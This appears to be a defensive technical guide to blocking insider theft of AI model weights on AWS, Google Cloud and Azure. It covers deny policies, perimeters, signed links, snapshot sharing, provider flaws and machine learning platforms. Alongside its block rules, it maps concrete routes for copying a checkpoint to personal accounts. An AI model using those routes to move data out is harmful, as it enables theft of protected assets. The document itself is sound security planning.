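Tenant restrictions are a feature of Microsoft Entra, Azure's identity system. They stop people on a company's network or devices from signing in to other organizations with outside accounts. If the researcher tries to sign in to her personal tenant on the test machine, the company's network or device software adds to her request a header that identifies the company's tenant and policy. Entra checks that policy, which blocks her personal tenant, and refuses the sign-in.

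Microsoft's *Set up tenant restrictions v2* describes three ways to add the header. A proxy can insert it into sign-in traffic, Windows can add it on managed devices, or the company can use Global Secure Access, Microsoft's service for routing and checking network traffic. The test machines probably run Linux, so the Windows option wouldn't help. A proxy has to decrypt the sign-in traffic to add the header. Entra doesn't enforce the restrictions when the header is missing, so the firewall also has to stop programs from bypassing the proxy.

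The restriction applies to signing in with an outside account, which leaves several other credentials available to the researcher:

| What she uses on the test machine | Do tenant restrictions stop it? |
|---|---|
| Her personal account, signing in to her personal tenant | Yes |
| Her work account, as a guest in her personal tenant | No |
| An access token that she obtained at home with her personal account | Not for Azure Storage |
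| A key for `herbackup`, or a signed access link to it | No, because she doesn't sign in |

The company can stop her from using her work account as a guest in other tenants by changing its outbound access settings, which control what its accounts may do there. In the weights tenant, these settings should block all outbound access by default.

Microsoft offers some protection against tokens obtained elsewhere, but only for SharePoint, Exchange and Microsoft Graph (an interface to data such as mail and user directories). According to Microsoft, the protection covers only Graph when used with Global Secure Access. An Azure Storage token obtained elsewhere would still work until it expired.

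The simplest way for an insider to get around tenant restrictions is to use the key to her own storage account. She can copy the key from her personal tenant at home, type it into the test machine and upload the checkpoint without contacting Entra. Tenant restrictions can still stop a careless insider, but only network controls can stop this upload.

### Two storage settings that work in different directions

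`AllowCrossTenantReplication` controls whether a storage account can take part in object replication with another tenant. Setting it to `false` prevents anyone from setting up replication between the weights account and `herbackup` in either direction. According to Microsoft, `false` is the default for accounts created after December 15, 2023. Older accounts allow cross-tenant replication unless someone has changed the setting, and an engineer has to delete any existing cross-tenant replication policies before changing it to `false`.

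An enforced perimeter already blocks replication, so the weights account's cross-tenant replication setting matters mainly if someone removes the account from the perimeter. Azure Policy can prevent people from creating accounts that allow this replication, or from changing an existing account to allow it.

`AllowedCopyScope` is easier to misread because it applies to the destination account and restricts where that account may copy from. It can limit the sources to accounts in the same tenant, or to accounts with private endpoints in the same network. On the weights account, it can block unwanted files from being copied in, but it doesn't stop anyone from copying the checkpoint out. Setting it on `herbackup` could block that copy, but the researcher controls that account, and the default allows copies from anywhere.

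The company can still get some protection from this setting by making the sandbox's storage accounts accept copies only from the main company tenant. Azure then refuses a direct copy from the weights tenant. In April 2026, Microsoft still described the setting as a preview and listed nine copy operations that it covers, which don't include downloading a file and then uploading it.

### Letting the scores out

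The release program is in the main company tenant, so even a score file has to cross between tenants. If the company gave the evaluation network a private endpoint to a storage account in the main tenant, the test machines would have a route out of the weights tenant, and only permissions would stop the researcher from copying the checkpoint through it.

It is safer for the release program to collect the scores. The evaluation program writes them to a separate storage account in the weights tenant, which the release network reaches through a private endpoint. The release program reads them with an identity that the weights tenant issued for this purpose. The Azure Policy rule on approvals has to allow the release subscription, but the company should assign that looser version only to the subscription that holds the scores. The version for the weights account still allows only the weights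 tenant's own subscriptions.

As on the other two clouds, only one machine identity, which researchers can't use, should be able to write to the scores account.

### Which combination protects the checkpoint

The table shows the main routes to the researcher's personal tenant. In the last four rows, she or an administrator helping her has the rights to set up the connection.

| Attempt | What stops it |
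|---|---|
| She tries to download the checkpoint at home with her work account | Enforced perimeter with no inbound rules |
| At home, she asks `herbackup` to fetch the checkpoint | Enforced perimeter with no inbound rules |
| She saves the checkpoint on the test machine and uploads it to `herbackup` with that account's key | Firewall |
| She uploads it through a private endpoint for `herbackup` in the evaluation network | Azure Policy rule on new endpoints |
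| She reads it from her personal tenant through a private endpoint for the weights account | Azure Policy rule on approvals |
| She sets up replication to `herbackup` | Enforced perimeter and the replication setting |
| She sets up a Data Factory job that writes to `herbackup` | Ban on Data Factory, or the rule for its endpoints |

The company therefore needs an enforced perimeter around the weights account, a firewall that blocks public storage addresses, and Azure Policy rules against private endpoints in both directions. It should also turn off cross-tenant replication and forbid Data Factory. Tenant restrictions and outbound access settings add a second layer against some uploads, but they can't replace the firewall.

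The same combination blocks a copy to the sandbox, because the sandbox is in a different tenant. It doesn't stop the researcher from copying the checkpoint to another storage account in the weights tenant if she has permission to write to that account.

An engineer can strengthen the weakest part by also routing private endpoint traffic through the firewall, which Microsoft recommends as a way to filter it by domain name. If someone then created an endpoint for `herbackup` despite the Azure Policy rule, the firewall could still block the upload.

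### Comparison with the AWS ownership test

The single ownership condition on AWS covers every outside account, including ones that don't exist yet. Azure's protections instead check indirect signs of ownership, such as a subscription ID, a domain name or the tenant where someone signs in, and these can become out of date. For example, if an administrator transfers an allowed subscription to another tenant, its ID stays the same and the Azure Policy rules still accept it.

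AWS tests ownership on each request, while Azure Policy checks a private endpoint when someone creates or approves it. If someone creates or approves a prohibited endpoint during a brief exemption, it keeps working after the exemption ends.

AWS has less of an advantage over Azure when the researcher uses personal credentials, because on AWS the company then also depends on its network, with an endpoint policy and a blocked public route to storage. Azure's nearest equivalent to that endpoint policy is a service endpoint policy, which also limits which storage a network may reach. But Microsoft says perimeters don't support service endpoint traffic, so the company can't use a service endpoint to reach a weights account inside an enforced perimeter.

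A company that can choose where to keep its weights will find cross-tenant copying easier to block on AWS. It can block the same copies on Azure, but doing so depends on more settings, and a single error in the firewall or in either private endpoint rule can let someone copy the checkpoint to an outside account.

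## Finding the services and calls that the rules miss

On all three clouds, the rules may miss some services, or some calls that give an outsider access to the checkpoint without copying it. The company needs to audit regularly for these gaps because the providers keep adding services.

### The coverage audit

The audit covers one environment at a time, starting with the four that use the weights.

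1. List every service the environment can use. Google Cloud enables services project by project, and `gcloud services list --enabled` shows them. Azure registers them by subscription, and `az provider list` shows which are registered. Most AWS services need no activation, so on AWS the list starts with everything AWS offers, minus whatever the SCPs deny.
2. Mark the services the perimeter supports, using the provider's current list.
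3. Disable the rest.
4. Examine every exception.

On AWS, the second step involves two separate checks: whether RCPs cover the service, and whether its calls supply `aws:ResourceOrgID`, the key that identifies the resource's owner. Part of the result for the evaluation account might look like this:

| Service | RCPs cover it | Calls supply the owner key | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| S3 | Yes | Yes | Keep |
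| KMS | Yes | Yes | Keep |
| EC2 (machines, disks and snapshots) | No | Most do | Keep, but deny calls that share data or connect accounts |
| Direct reading and writing of snapshots | No | None do | Deny |
| Lambda (runs small programs on demand) | No | Yes | Deny |
| Bedrock (runs AI models) | No | Yes | Deny |

For the third step, the company should list the services it permits and deny everything else. This SCP statement does that for the weights unit, although a real list would be longer:

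```json
{
  "Sid": "OnlyListedServices",
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "NotAction": ["s3:*", "kms:*", "ec2:*", "ecr:*", "iam:*", "logs:*", "sts:*"],
  "Resource": "*"
}
```

`NotAction` makes the denial apply to every action except those listed, including actions of services that AWS hasn't launched yet. A list of forbidden services would need an update for each launch. For example, AWS now accepts Bedrock API keys at two endpoints and controls each with a separate action, so a company that denies only the older action leaves the newer endpoint open. Google Cloud has an organization policy that restricts which services projects may use, and Azure Policy can restrict which types of resources people create.

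Enabling a service can also change what existing credentials can do. The Hacker News' *Thousands of Public Google Cloud API Keys Exposed with Gemini Access* (2026) reports that the security company Truffle Security found 2,863 live Google API keys on public websites. Developers had published keys like these for uses such as embedding maps. When someone enabled the API for Gemini, Google's AI model, in the same project, the keys began to work for Gemini too, which could expose uploaded files. Nobody had edited the keys, so a review of permission changes wouldn't have caught the problem. Google has since started blocking leaked keys from accessing Gemini.

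The fourth step covers every ingress and egress rule, every entry under `NotAction` or `NotResource`, every tag that exempts an identity, and every Azure Policy exemption. For each exception, the auditor should record who can use it, where it lets data go, and what else would stop someone from sending weights through it. If nobody can say which task needs it, the company should delete it.

Lagonsin (2026), in *Google updates VPC Service Controls with new policy tools*, reports that administrators can now specify folders and whole organizations in Google's ingress and egress rules. An exception that looks narrow could therefore cover every project a partner owns. The same update lets administrators include a folder in a perimeter, which should help protect new projects that nobody remembers to add.

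### Calls that don't supply the tested key

The SCP that limits staff to company resources also blocks calls that never supply `aws:ResourceOrgID`, even when the resource belongs to the company. AWS's list of these calls includes every direct call to Elastic Block Store (EBS, the AWS virtual disk service) and several EC2 calls that connect one account's network to another's. One of these EC2 calls is `ec2:CreateVpcEndpoint`, so the SCP would stop engineers from creating the endpoints that the perimeter depends on.

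An engineer who runs into this will probably exempt the whole service, and the SCP will stop checking ownership for all of that service's calls. This is risky because many of the calls on AWS's list link accounts, for instance by accepting a network connection or a shared directory.

The company should instead exempt individual actions and let only one role perform them. Network engineers then have to switch to that role or wait for someone who has it whenever they need a new endpoint.

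The weights unit needs no exemption for direct EBS calls. AWS's *Actions, resources, and condition keys for Amazon Elastic Block Store* lists six actions, including `GetSnapshotBlock`, which returns part of a snapshot's data. A policy can restrict them by tag, parent snapshot or disk size, but AWS lists no condition key for the snapshot's owner. Leaving them blocked breaks backup products that read snapshots through these calls. AWS also publishes the list in machine-readable form, so a script can compare it with last month's and report new actions.

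### Calls that involve two resources

Some calls use one resource to create another, and a rule that checks only the new resource can miss where the data came from. Before October 2024, AWS had this gap for disk snapshots.

Suppose someone in the evaluation account saves the weights to a disk, takes a snapshot and lets the sandbox account use it. The researcher then uses her sandbox identity to create a disk from that snapshot. To prevent this, the company has attached an SCP with this statement to the sandbox account:

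```json
{
  "Sid": "NoDisksFromWeightsSnapshots",
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "Action": ["ec2:CreateVolume", "ec2:CopySnapshot"],
  "Resource": "*",
  "Condition": {
    "StringEquals": {
      "aws:ResourceAccount": [
        "111111111111", "222222222222",
        "333333333333", "444444444444"
      ]
    }
  }
}
```

Her request involves the snapshot she starts from and the disk she creates:

| Resource | Owner | Before the change | Since the change |
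|---|---|---|---|
| New disk | Sandbox, 666666666666 | AWS checks the owner and finds no match | Same |
| Source snapshot | Evaluation, 333333333333 | AWS doesn't check the owner | AWS checks the owner, finds a match and refuses the request |

Before the change, the same statement would have had no effect on her request. According to *Amazon EBS will support AWS global condition keys and seven EC2-specific keys*, a thread on the AWS re:Post question-and-answer forum, AWS did not evaluate any of the global keys in policies for the source snapshot when someone created a disk or copied a snapshot. It also did not evaluate seven EC2 keys, such as the one that shows whether the snapshot is encrypted.

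The change also made existing rules stricter. In an example from AWS re:Post, a company's rule denying unencrypted disks now applies to unencrypted source snapshots too. The snapshots behind most public machine images are unencrypted, so ordinary machines could fail to start. A rule on ownership can also stop them from starting, because those images belong to someone else. The company can avoid both problems by keeping encrypted copies of approved images in its own account, but it then has to renew the copies with every security update.

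The failures can be hard to recognize in the logs because AWS may record a refused disk under `RunInstances`, the call that starts a machine. AWS re:Post advises searching for all failed EC2 calls.

To find similar gaps, the auditor can list every call that copies, restores, imports or exports data, and test each one with an outside resource first as the source and then as the destination. This takes time, and the company has to repeat it when the provider changes how a call works.

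### Calls that share access instead of copying

On AWS, the owner of a snapshot can let another account use it by adding that account's number to a list. Sharing doesn't copy any data, and the only resource in the request is the company's own snapshot, so the SCP's ownership check passes. The outside account can then copy the snapshot under its own identity, which the company's SCPs don't cover. RCPs don't cover snapshots either.

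The simplest control is an SCP on the weights unit that denies `ec2:ModifySnapshotAttribute` and `ec2:ModifyImageAttribute`, the calls for sharing snapshots and machine images. Teams that share images between accounts would then have to share them from an account outside the weights unit.

As a second control, the company can encrypt every disk in the unit with its own KMS key. An outside account can't read a shared snapshot without using that key, and the RCP on KMS described earlier blocks outside accounts from using it. The company also has to stop people from creating unencrypted disks, or someone could move the weights to one and share its snapshot. Every machine then needs permission to use the key, and if the company loses the key, it can no longer read the disks.

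Native suggests addressing some of these gaps with AWS's declarative policies, which enforce a set configuration for services such as EC2. Such a policy can turn off public sharing of snapshots, but it doesn't stop someone from sharing one with a specific account.

On Google Cloud, sharing is less of a problem for protected services. If someone gives an outside identity permission to use a company snapshot, that identity's request still has to cross the perimeter, and Google refuses it unless a rule allows it. On Azure, a network security perimeter doesn't cover disks, and a person with the right permission can export one through a signed link. The company can block exports by using Azure Policy to require that every disk's network access setting is `DenyAll`, but engineers then can't download a disk to examine it after a failure.

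### Signed links

Anyone who has an AWS presigned URL, or its equivalent on Google Cloud or Azure, can use it without logging in until it expires. An access review that lists people and their permissions won't show who has one.

If the researcher creates a link to the checkpoint at work and opens it at home, the result depends on the cloud:

| Cloud | Whose authority the link carries | What stops the download | What else the company can do |
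|---|---|---|---|
| AWS | The identity that created it | The RCP that accepts downloads only through the company's endpoints | Require credentials in the request's header |
| Google Cloud | Usually a service account | The perimeter, if no ingress rule or access level admits the request | Forbid downloadable service account keys and restrict who may sign |
| Azure | The storage account's key, or a signed-in user | An enforced perimeter with no inbound rules | Turn off access by account key |

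On AWS, the resource control policy (RCP) against outside identities doesn't stop someone from using a signed link, because AWS treats the request as coming from the researcher's work identity. The company therefore relies on its network rule. Native describes a ready-made RCP in AWS Control Tower, CT.S3.PV.2, that allows only requests with credentials in the header. This disables signed links for the company's buckets, so any tool that provides downloads through such links will stop working.

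Google's perimeter checks where a request comes from as well as who makes it, so a signed link shouldn't get the researcher past it. An ingress rule with `ANY_IDENTITY` that covers her network could still let the download through, which is another reason to keep such rules out of the weights perimeter. Forbidding service account keys means programs outside Google Cloud need another way to prove their identity.

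Azure's links need the most attention. A link signed with the storage account's key isn't tied to any person and can last for years. If the researcher leaves the company, the link keeps working until it expires or someone replaces the key. Setting `AllowSharedKeyAccess` to `false` on the weights account makes Azure reject both the key and links signed with it. Software that connects with the key then has to switch to Entra sign-in. Users can still sign links, but those last at most seven days.

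These settings apply only to the company's own storage, so network controls still have to block uploads through a link to the researcher's personal bucket.

### Requests a cloud service makes under its own identity

A backup service may need to read a disk at night, when no employee is logged in, so it uses its own identity. A perimeter rule written for employees may not apply to that identity.

AWS services use several kinds of identity, and a policy can't treat them all alike. `aws:PrincipalIsAWSService` is true only when a service calls under AWS's own name, as the audit log service CloudTrail does when it writes to a bucket. According to AWS, the key is false when the service uses a role in the customer's account. These roles include service-linked roles, each of which AWS defines for a particular service. Native points out that RCPs don't apply to service-linked roles, and that services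 such as AWS Backup and AWS Config, which records changes to resources, rely on them. SCPs don't restrict these roles either.

The company therefore has to control who can set up these services and what the services can do. In the weights unit, it can deny `iam:CreateServiceLinkedRole` except for approved services and deny changes to the services' settings. The company then loses some convenient tools and may have to run its own backups of the checkpoint. Training platforms are harder to restrict because they rely heavily on service identities.

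Sometimes the provider itself checks the wrong identity. In 2026, Google corrected two services that retrieved stored passwords after checking only the service's own permission. They now also check the requester's permission. A customer can limit the damage from such errors by giving each service identity as little access as possible, but must then maintain more identities.

### Logs and metadata

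Logs and resource names can reveal information to people who have no access to the data itself. A password or an encryption key fits easily in one log record, but logs are a poor route for weights because moving 100 GB would take 100 million records if each held 1 kilobyte.

The company should send logs only to accounts it owns, restrict who can read them, and set an alert for unusual volume. It should also keep model names out of bucket names and tags. Developers will find it harder to debug programs when they can't read the logs freely.

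Missing records are also a problem. If the researcher uses personal credentials on a test machine to reach her own bucket, the ordinary record of that call may go only to her account. In February 2025, AWS (2025) made network activity events generally available. They let the owner of a VPC endpoint record the calls that pass through it, including those its policy denies. AWS's *Logging network activity events* explains that the owner has to enable them for each service and pay extra. *How to use the new CloudTrail network activity events*, by the cloud security vendor Wiz, gives a price of about $0.10 per 100,000 events. Reading the 1 TB checkpoint in 8-megabyte pieces takes 125,000 calls, which would cost about 13 cents to log.

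### Published flaws

The gaps above come from how the services work. Providers also make mistakes, and these are the published ones that weakened a perimeter control:

- On September 10, 2024, AWS announced changes to how CloudTrail delivers records of denied requests, to close a leak that Tracebit's *Breaching the Data Perimeter* describes.
- On December 6, 2024, Google Cloud's *Security bulletins* for its AI platform reported a medium-severity flaw (GCP-2024-063, or CVE-2024-12236) in the API that serves Gemini, which allowed data to bypass VPC Service Controls until Google made the API reject the affected requests.
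- In June 2025, AWS fixed a flaw in its logging of denied requests that exposed which account owned a bucket, as Varonis' *The Silent Attackers* reports.
- In January 2026, AWS fixed a flaw in a new Bedrock endpoint that did not fully enforce SCPs for requests made with long-term API keys, which Sonrai Security's *Cracks in the Bedrock* had identified.

Other bulletins concern services that a company might use inside a perimeter. The table covers 2026 entries from the general edition of Google Cloud's *Security bulletins* and one bulletin from AWS (2026).

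| Date | Service | Severity | Flaw and fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| February 20 | Vertex AI Experiments (Google) | High | An outsider could steal models from other customers; Google fixed this in version 1.133.0. |
| March 16 | Bedrock AgentCore Starter Toolkit (AWS) | Important | The toolkit didn't verify who owned a bucket; AWS fixed this in version 0.1.13. |
| June 22 | Cloud Logging (Google) | Medium | Exported logs could go to an outsider; Google gives the details in a separate bulletin. |
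| June 24 | Cloud Build (Google) | Low | The service checked only its own permission to read secrets; it now checks the caller's too. |
| June 24 | Firebase Studio (Google) | High | Users could download other customers' source code; Google has fixed the service. |
| July 13 | BigQuery, Dataform and Colab Enterprise (Google) | Critical | A missing check allowed users to take over other customers' code repositories; Google has fixed the services. |
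| July 13 | Developer Connect (Google) | Medium | This was the same flaw as in Cloud Build, with the same fix. |

Several flaws involved software that trusted a bucket by its name without checking who owned it. SC Media's *Google Cloud Vertex AI SDK flaw allowed model hijacking and code execution* describes another, in which a Google programming toolkit could upload a customer's model to an outsider's bucket. Google added ownership checks and put random identifiers in the bucket names. In a separate bulletin, AWS (2026) tells customers to check that they own any bucket with a predictable name, because upgrading the software doesn't recover a name someone else has already taken.

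A perimeter is a useful second defense here. If the toolkit ran on the researcher's test machine and selected an outsider's bucket, the egress check on Google Cloud or the ownership condition on AWS should block the upload. Engineers can also specify the bucket themselves, which takes almost no effort.

Google pays outside researchers to look for flaws in its perimeter. The Google Cloud Vulnerability Reward Program opened in October 2024 with VPC Service Controls in its top tier (Winstead, 2024, *Think Outside the Perimeter*). The program rewards researchers who find ways to move protected data out, get around access controls, or combine several services to do either. Winstead also encourages researchers to look beyond storage, because the perimeter protects more than 100 services. Google has to apply the same rules correctly across all of their code.

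Providers had fixed nearly all of these flaws by the time they became public, but new services are more of a concern. The Bedrock flaw lasted a little over seven weeks, from December 4, 2025 to January 26, 2026, according to the network security vendor Aviatrix. A company that relied on SCPs alone would have had a gap during those weeks, even if it had written them correctly. AWS (2026) added private network access to the same endpoint only on February 12, although the older Bedrock endpoint already had it. Blocking the endpoint's public address would have closed the gap, so it is worth keeping the network controls even where an SCP seems sufficient.

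### What the bulletins leave out

Public bulletins don't show how many flaws researchers or attackers have found. Providers can often fix a service without customers doing anything, and outsiders can't tell how many fixes they never announce. Winstead says Google credits a valid report on its public page if the finder asks, so that page isn't a complete list either.

The bulletins also contain little information about whether anyone exploited a flaw. Aviatrix reports that AWS confirmed the Bedrock problem affected no customers, but customers can check this only if their own logs recorded the relevant calls. Google's summaries of the 2026 flaws in the table don't mention VPC Service Controls, so a customer can't tell from them whether a perimeter would have helped.

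A security bulletin can also come out long after the fix. One Google Cloud bulletin describes a high-severity flaw in Integration Connectors, a service that links Google Cloud to other software. A user could exploit the flaw to take over a project. Google patched it on December 11, 2025, but apparently didn't publish the bulletin until September 2026.

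## Covering managed machine learning platforms and model registries

A managed machine learning platform trains, stores and runs models on the provider's machines. Examples are Google Cloud's Vertex AI, AWS's SageMaker and Bedrock, and Azure Machine Learning. These platforms are the hardest services for a perimeter to cover because the provider may own the network, the storage and the identity behind each request, and the rules described so far work best when the company owns all three.

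Suppose the researcher starts a fine-tuning job, which trains the finished model further on new data. The job's machines may have their own route to the internet. The job may run under a service identity that can read files she can't. The platform may save the tuned model in a bucket missing from the company's inventory.

In the Gemini flaw of December 2024, listed earlier, users could give Gemini the web address of a media file to read, and Google Cloud says that someone inside the perimeter could encode sensitive data in that address. Stealing a terabyte this way would be slow, but the customer's firewall couldn't stop the request to the outside site because it came from Google's service.

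### Vertex AI

Vertex AI became part of Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform on April 22, 2026, according to Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes*, but many guides and permissions still use the old name. Google Cloud says that if the perimeter protects `aiplatform.googleapis.com`, training data, the customer's own models and batch job results can't leave it. The perimeter also closes the platform's public interface, which otherwise accepts requests from authorized callers anywhere on the internet.

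The internet route depends on how the engineer connects Google's machines to the company's network. The older method, peering, links the two networks. Google's side keeps a default route to the internet and to all Google services until the engineer runs this command:

```
gcloud services vpc-peerings enable-vpc-service-controls \
  --network=training-network --service=servicenetworking.googleapis.com
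```

It removes the route and directs Google's service names to the restricted range. The newer method, a Private Service Connect interface, is safer because the perimeter blocks the internet by default. Google Cloud's *Use Private Service Connect interface for Vertex AI Training* explains that each job request has to name the connection. A job that doesn't name it can't reach the company's network, but should still have no internet route.

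The company should create the perimeter before deploying anything, because an AI agent deployed earlier keeps its internet access, and an endpoint (the address where a model receives queries) created earlier won't accept new models. Researchers should also avoid custom kernels in Workbench, Google's notebook service, because these kernels need the wider address range, 199.36.153.8/30, which the firewall should block.

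Working inside the perimeter is less convenient. Jobs can't download Python packages from the public index, so engineers have to build them into the container image or keep them in a company repository. Vertex AI's logging of requests and responses doesn't work there either.

#### What the service identities can read

By default, a training job runs under an identity that Google manages, the Custom Code Service Agent. Google Cloud's *Agent Platform access control with IAM* calls the permission to create these jobs "highly privileged", because it effectively gives editor-level access to other services in the project, including Cloud Storage. A researcher who can't open a bucket in the training project could start a job whose code opens it. The company should therefore treat everyone who can create jobs as able to copy any weights stored in the project.

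Google recommends replacing the default identity. It gave this advice after Unit 42, a security research team, found a way to reach some of Google's proprietary code through Vertex AI (The Hacker News, 2026). An engineer can specify a custom service account for each job, but according to Google Cloud, the platform still uses its own identity to fetch container images and to access Cloud Storage during batch inference, when a model processes many inputs in one job.

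The location of the weights matters more, because the researcher could leave the custom account out of her request. Google's service agents can't read a bucket in another project unless someone grants them access. If the company keeps all weights, including fine-tuned ones, in project 101, a job in project 102 that runs under the default identity can't open them.

#### Registering, exporting and copying a model

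Vertex AI's model registry lists models and their versions. When someone registers a model from files in a bucket, Google copies the files to a second bucket, which Google manages, so deleting the original files doesn't delete all the weights. Google Cloud's *Custom container requirements for inference* adds that a custom account used for serving automatically gets read access to the second bucket.

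Exporting a model requires the `aiplatform.models.export` permission. The ordinary Vertex AI User role includes it, judging by the instructions in Google Cloud's *Copy a model in Vertex AI Model Registry*. Researchers who only send questions to a model should have a custom role whose sole permission is `aiplatform.endpoints.predict`.

To copy a model to another project, the source project's owner first gives the destination's service identity permission to export. The caller then sends the request to the destination project and needs permission to upload models there, according to Google Cloud's *Method: models.copy*. So if the researcher persuades an administrator of the training project to grant the export permission, she can request the copy from her personal project, where she has the permissions she needs.

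The perimeter should block this copy, because Google lists customers' models among the things that can't leave. But Google's documentation is inconsistent about whether models can be copied between projects. The guide explains how to do it, while the reference page says the source model must be in the same project. A company that uses the registry should try copying a harmless model to the sandbox and to an outside project, and confirm that both attempts fail.

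### SageMaker

SageMaker Studio is a web workspace where researchers write code and start jobs. In VPC-only mode, Studio's traffic goes through the company's network, but AWS's *Network management* warns that jobs started from Studio don't inherit this setting. AWS's *Run Training and Inference Containers in Internet-Free Mode* says that training and serving containers can reach the internet by default, so a job can too if the researcher leaves the network settings out of her request.

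Two settings on a SageMaker job control its network access. `VpcConfig` connects the job to the company's network. Network isolation blocks all calls into or out of the container, including calls to other AWS services, and withholds AWS credentials from it, according to Cloudaware's *SageMaker models should have network isolation enabled*, a vendor's copy of an AWS security check. AWS explains that SageMaker then fetches the files from S3 and sends the logs from outside the container.

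| Settings on the job | What the researcher's code can reach | How SageMaker reads the weights bucket |
|---|---|---|
| Neither | The internet | Outside the company's network |
| `VpcConfig` only | Whatever the company's network allows | Through the company's network |
| Isolation only | Nothing | Outside the company's network |
| Both | Nothing | Through the company's network |

Jobs that handle weights need both. Isolation alone would keep the code offline, but the weights bucket would refuse the download, because its resource control policy accepts reads only through the company's endpoints. This SCP for the weights unit makes both settings compulsory:

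```json
{
  "Version": "2012-10-17",
  "Statement": [
    {
      "Sid": "RequireIsolation",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": ["sagemaker:CreateTrainingJob", "sagemaker:CreateModel"],
      "Resource": "*",
      "Condition": {
        "BoolIfExists": { "sagemaker:NetworkIsolation": "false" }
      }
    },
    {
      "Sid": "RequireCompanyNetwork",
      "Effect": "Deny",
      "Action": ["sagemaker:CreateTrainingJob", "sagemaker:CreateModel"],
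      "Resource": "*",
      "Condition": {
        "Null": { "sagemaker:VpcSubnets": "true" }
      }
    }
  ]
}
```

The weights unit's list of permitted services leaves out SageMaker, so an engineer has to add it before any job can run. Adding only the actions the job needs is safer than adding `sagemaker:*`, which would also allow notebooks and other job types that this SCP doesn't check.

Even an isolated job has one way to send data out. The researcher chooses the S3 location where SageMaker saves the result, and she could enter her personal bucket. SageMaker makes that upload under a role in the company's account, so the SCP that limits company identities to company resources blocks it. The weights unit's own SCP blocks an upload to the sandbox.

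### JumpStart buckets and Bedrock

JumpStart is SageMaker's collection of pre-trained models. AWS keeps the files in its own buckets, one for each region, with names like `jumpstart-cache-prod-us-east-1`. The SCP would block access to these buckets because they don't belong to the company, so AWS's sample policy exempts them with `NotResource`.

The sample is broader than necessary. It exempts the buckets from the ownership check for every action, including uploads, although researchers only need to download. It also identifies the buckets by name and doesn't check who owns them, as it does for a partner's bucket. A company that uses JumpStart should name only the regions it uses, avoid wildcards, and add this statement:

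```json
{
  "Sid": "JumpStartReadOnly",
  "Effect": "Deny",
  "NotAction": ["s3:GetObject", "s3:ListBucket"],
  "Resource": [
    "arn:aws:s3:::jumpstart-cache-prod-us-east-1",
    "arn:aws:s3:::jumpstart-cache-prod-us-east-1/*"
  ]
}
```

The endpoint policy needs the same restriction, since AWS's sample also allows every action. The weights unit needs no exemption, because its jobs start from the company's own checkpoint.

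Bedrock runs models for customers on machines they can't see. Its custom model import feature reads weights from a customer's bucket and makes a copy that Bedrock manages. Customers can query the imported model but can't inspect the storage that holds the copy. Bedrock also lets customers share some custom models with other accounts through Resource Access Manager, AWS's general sharing service, and the recipient then copies the model into its own account.

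The weights unit's list of permitted services leaves out Bedrock and Resource Access Manager, and the company should keep both off the list. Importing into Bedrock might suit a smaller model whose loss would do the company little harm. For the main checkpoint, it would save the work of running a server but add a copy of the weights and a way to share them.

### Azure Machine Learning

Azure Machine Learning groups jobs, data and settings into workspaces. A workspace can have a managed network, which Microsoft runs for the customer's jobs. Microsoft's *Plan for network isolation* describes one mode that allows all outgoing internet traffic and another that allows only approved destinations. The weights tenant should use the second mode. Microsoft's *Secure managed online endpoints by using network isolation* explains that this mode also covers models that are answering queries.

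Researchers then lose direct access to public packages and models. Microsoft's *Workspace managed virtual network isolation* says they have to prepare everything a job needs in their private environment. Azure adds the destinations that the platform requires, so the company's own list doesn't include every allowed destination.

The protection depends on what the company approves. Microsoft's *Azure Machine Learning data exfiltration prevention* sorts destinations by whether a malicious insider could write to them. It treats Entra, Azure's management interface and Microsoft's public container registry as safe, and warns about two others:

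- Azure Storage, where the insider could have an account of her own. The company should approve only private endpoints to its own accounts.
- Azure Front Door, which delivers websites for many customers. Microsoft recommends replacing its general entry with the two domain names that Azure Machine Learning needs.

Microsoft may understate the risk of the management interface. Every Azure customer uses it, so the researcher could sign in to her personal subscription and store small pieces of data in its settings. Moving 100 GB this way would take very many requests, and the tenant restrictions described earlier would block the sign-in if the job's traffic passed through them.

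Approved private endpoints need a separate check because the Azure Policy rule against endpoints to outside accounts probably doesn't cover those a workspace creates in its managed network, just as it doesn't cover Data Factory's. Only the team that runs the perimeter should be able to edit a workspace's outbound rules.

A company can also run the jobs in its own network. The machines still need access to some storage accounts that belong to Microsoft, so Microsoft suggests a service endpoint policy that allows the workspace's default storage account and `/services/Azure/MachineLearning`, an alias for Microsoft's accounts. Like the JumpStart exemption, the alias allows access to provider-owned storage that the company can't inspect. The jobs can still reach the weights account through a private endpoint, because private endpoints and service endpoint policies work independently.

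Some parts of the platform stay outside either network. To preview data in the web interface, Microsoft's managed service reads the workspace's storage under its own identity, according to Microsoft's *Network traffic flow when using a secured workspace*. The customer can allow this access for one workspace or for a list of trusted Microsoft services. The storage account that holds the weights shouldn't be the workspace's default storage, so that nobody has a reason to grant either kind of access to it. Previews of the weights won't work, but nobody needs them.

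### Registries and public hubs

Container registries and model registries exist to make sharing easy, so the company should treat each one as it treats the weights bucket. These are the main ways for a model to leave one:

| Registry | How a model could leave | Control |
|---|---|---|
| Google Artifact Registry | An outside identity downloads an image | The service perimeter |
| AWS Elastic Container Registry | The repository's policy lets an outside account download | The RCP for that service |
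| AWS Elastic Container Registry | A replication rule copies new images to an outside account | Deny `ecr:PutReplicationConfiguration` |
| SageMaker model registry | A policy shares the entry with an outside account | Deny `sagemaker:PutModelPackageGroupPolicy` |
| Azure Container Registry | Someone imports the image into another registry | Disable public access and the registry's export setting |
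| Azure Machine Learning registry | Another workspace uses the shared model | Forbid these registries in the weights tenant |

AWS runs replication under a service-linked role, which the policies don't restrict, so the company has to stop people from setting up replication. Sharing an entry in SageMaker's registry is less serious because the entry only points to files in S3, and the RCP on the bucket still keeps the outside account from reading them.

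A downloaded model or package can contain malicious code, which would run next to the weights, while uploading a model can itself be the theft. Some sources allow only downloads. For example, Google Cloud lists more than 30 repositories of its own container images that every project can read, whatever its perimeter, but that customers can't write to.

Anyone can publish a model on public hubs such as Hugging Face. If a firewall rule admits a hub's domain name so that researchers can download models, a researcher can also upload a checkpoint to her own page there. The cloud provider's ownership checks don't apply to the hub, as with any third-party site. A proxy could decrypt the traffic and block uploads, but it is simpler to block the hub from the weights network. A program in another project can download the models researchers request, scan them and copy them to a mirror inside the boundary,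 though researchers then wait longer for new models.

AWS's *Security Hub CSPM controls for SageMaker AI* includes a check that models get their containers from a private registry inside the company's network. The company can use this check to find jobs that bypass the registry.

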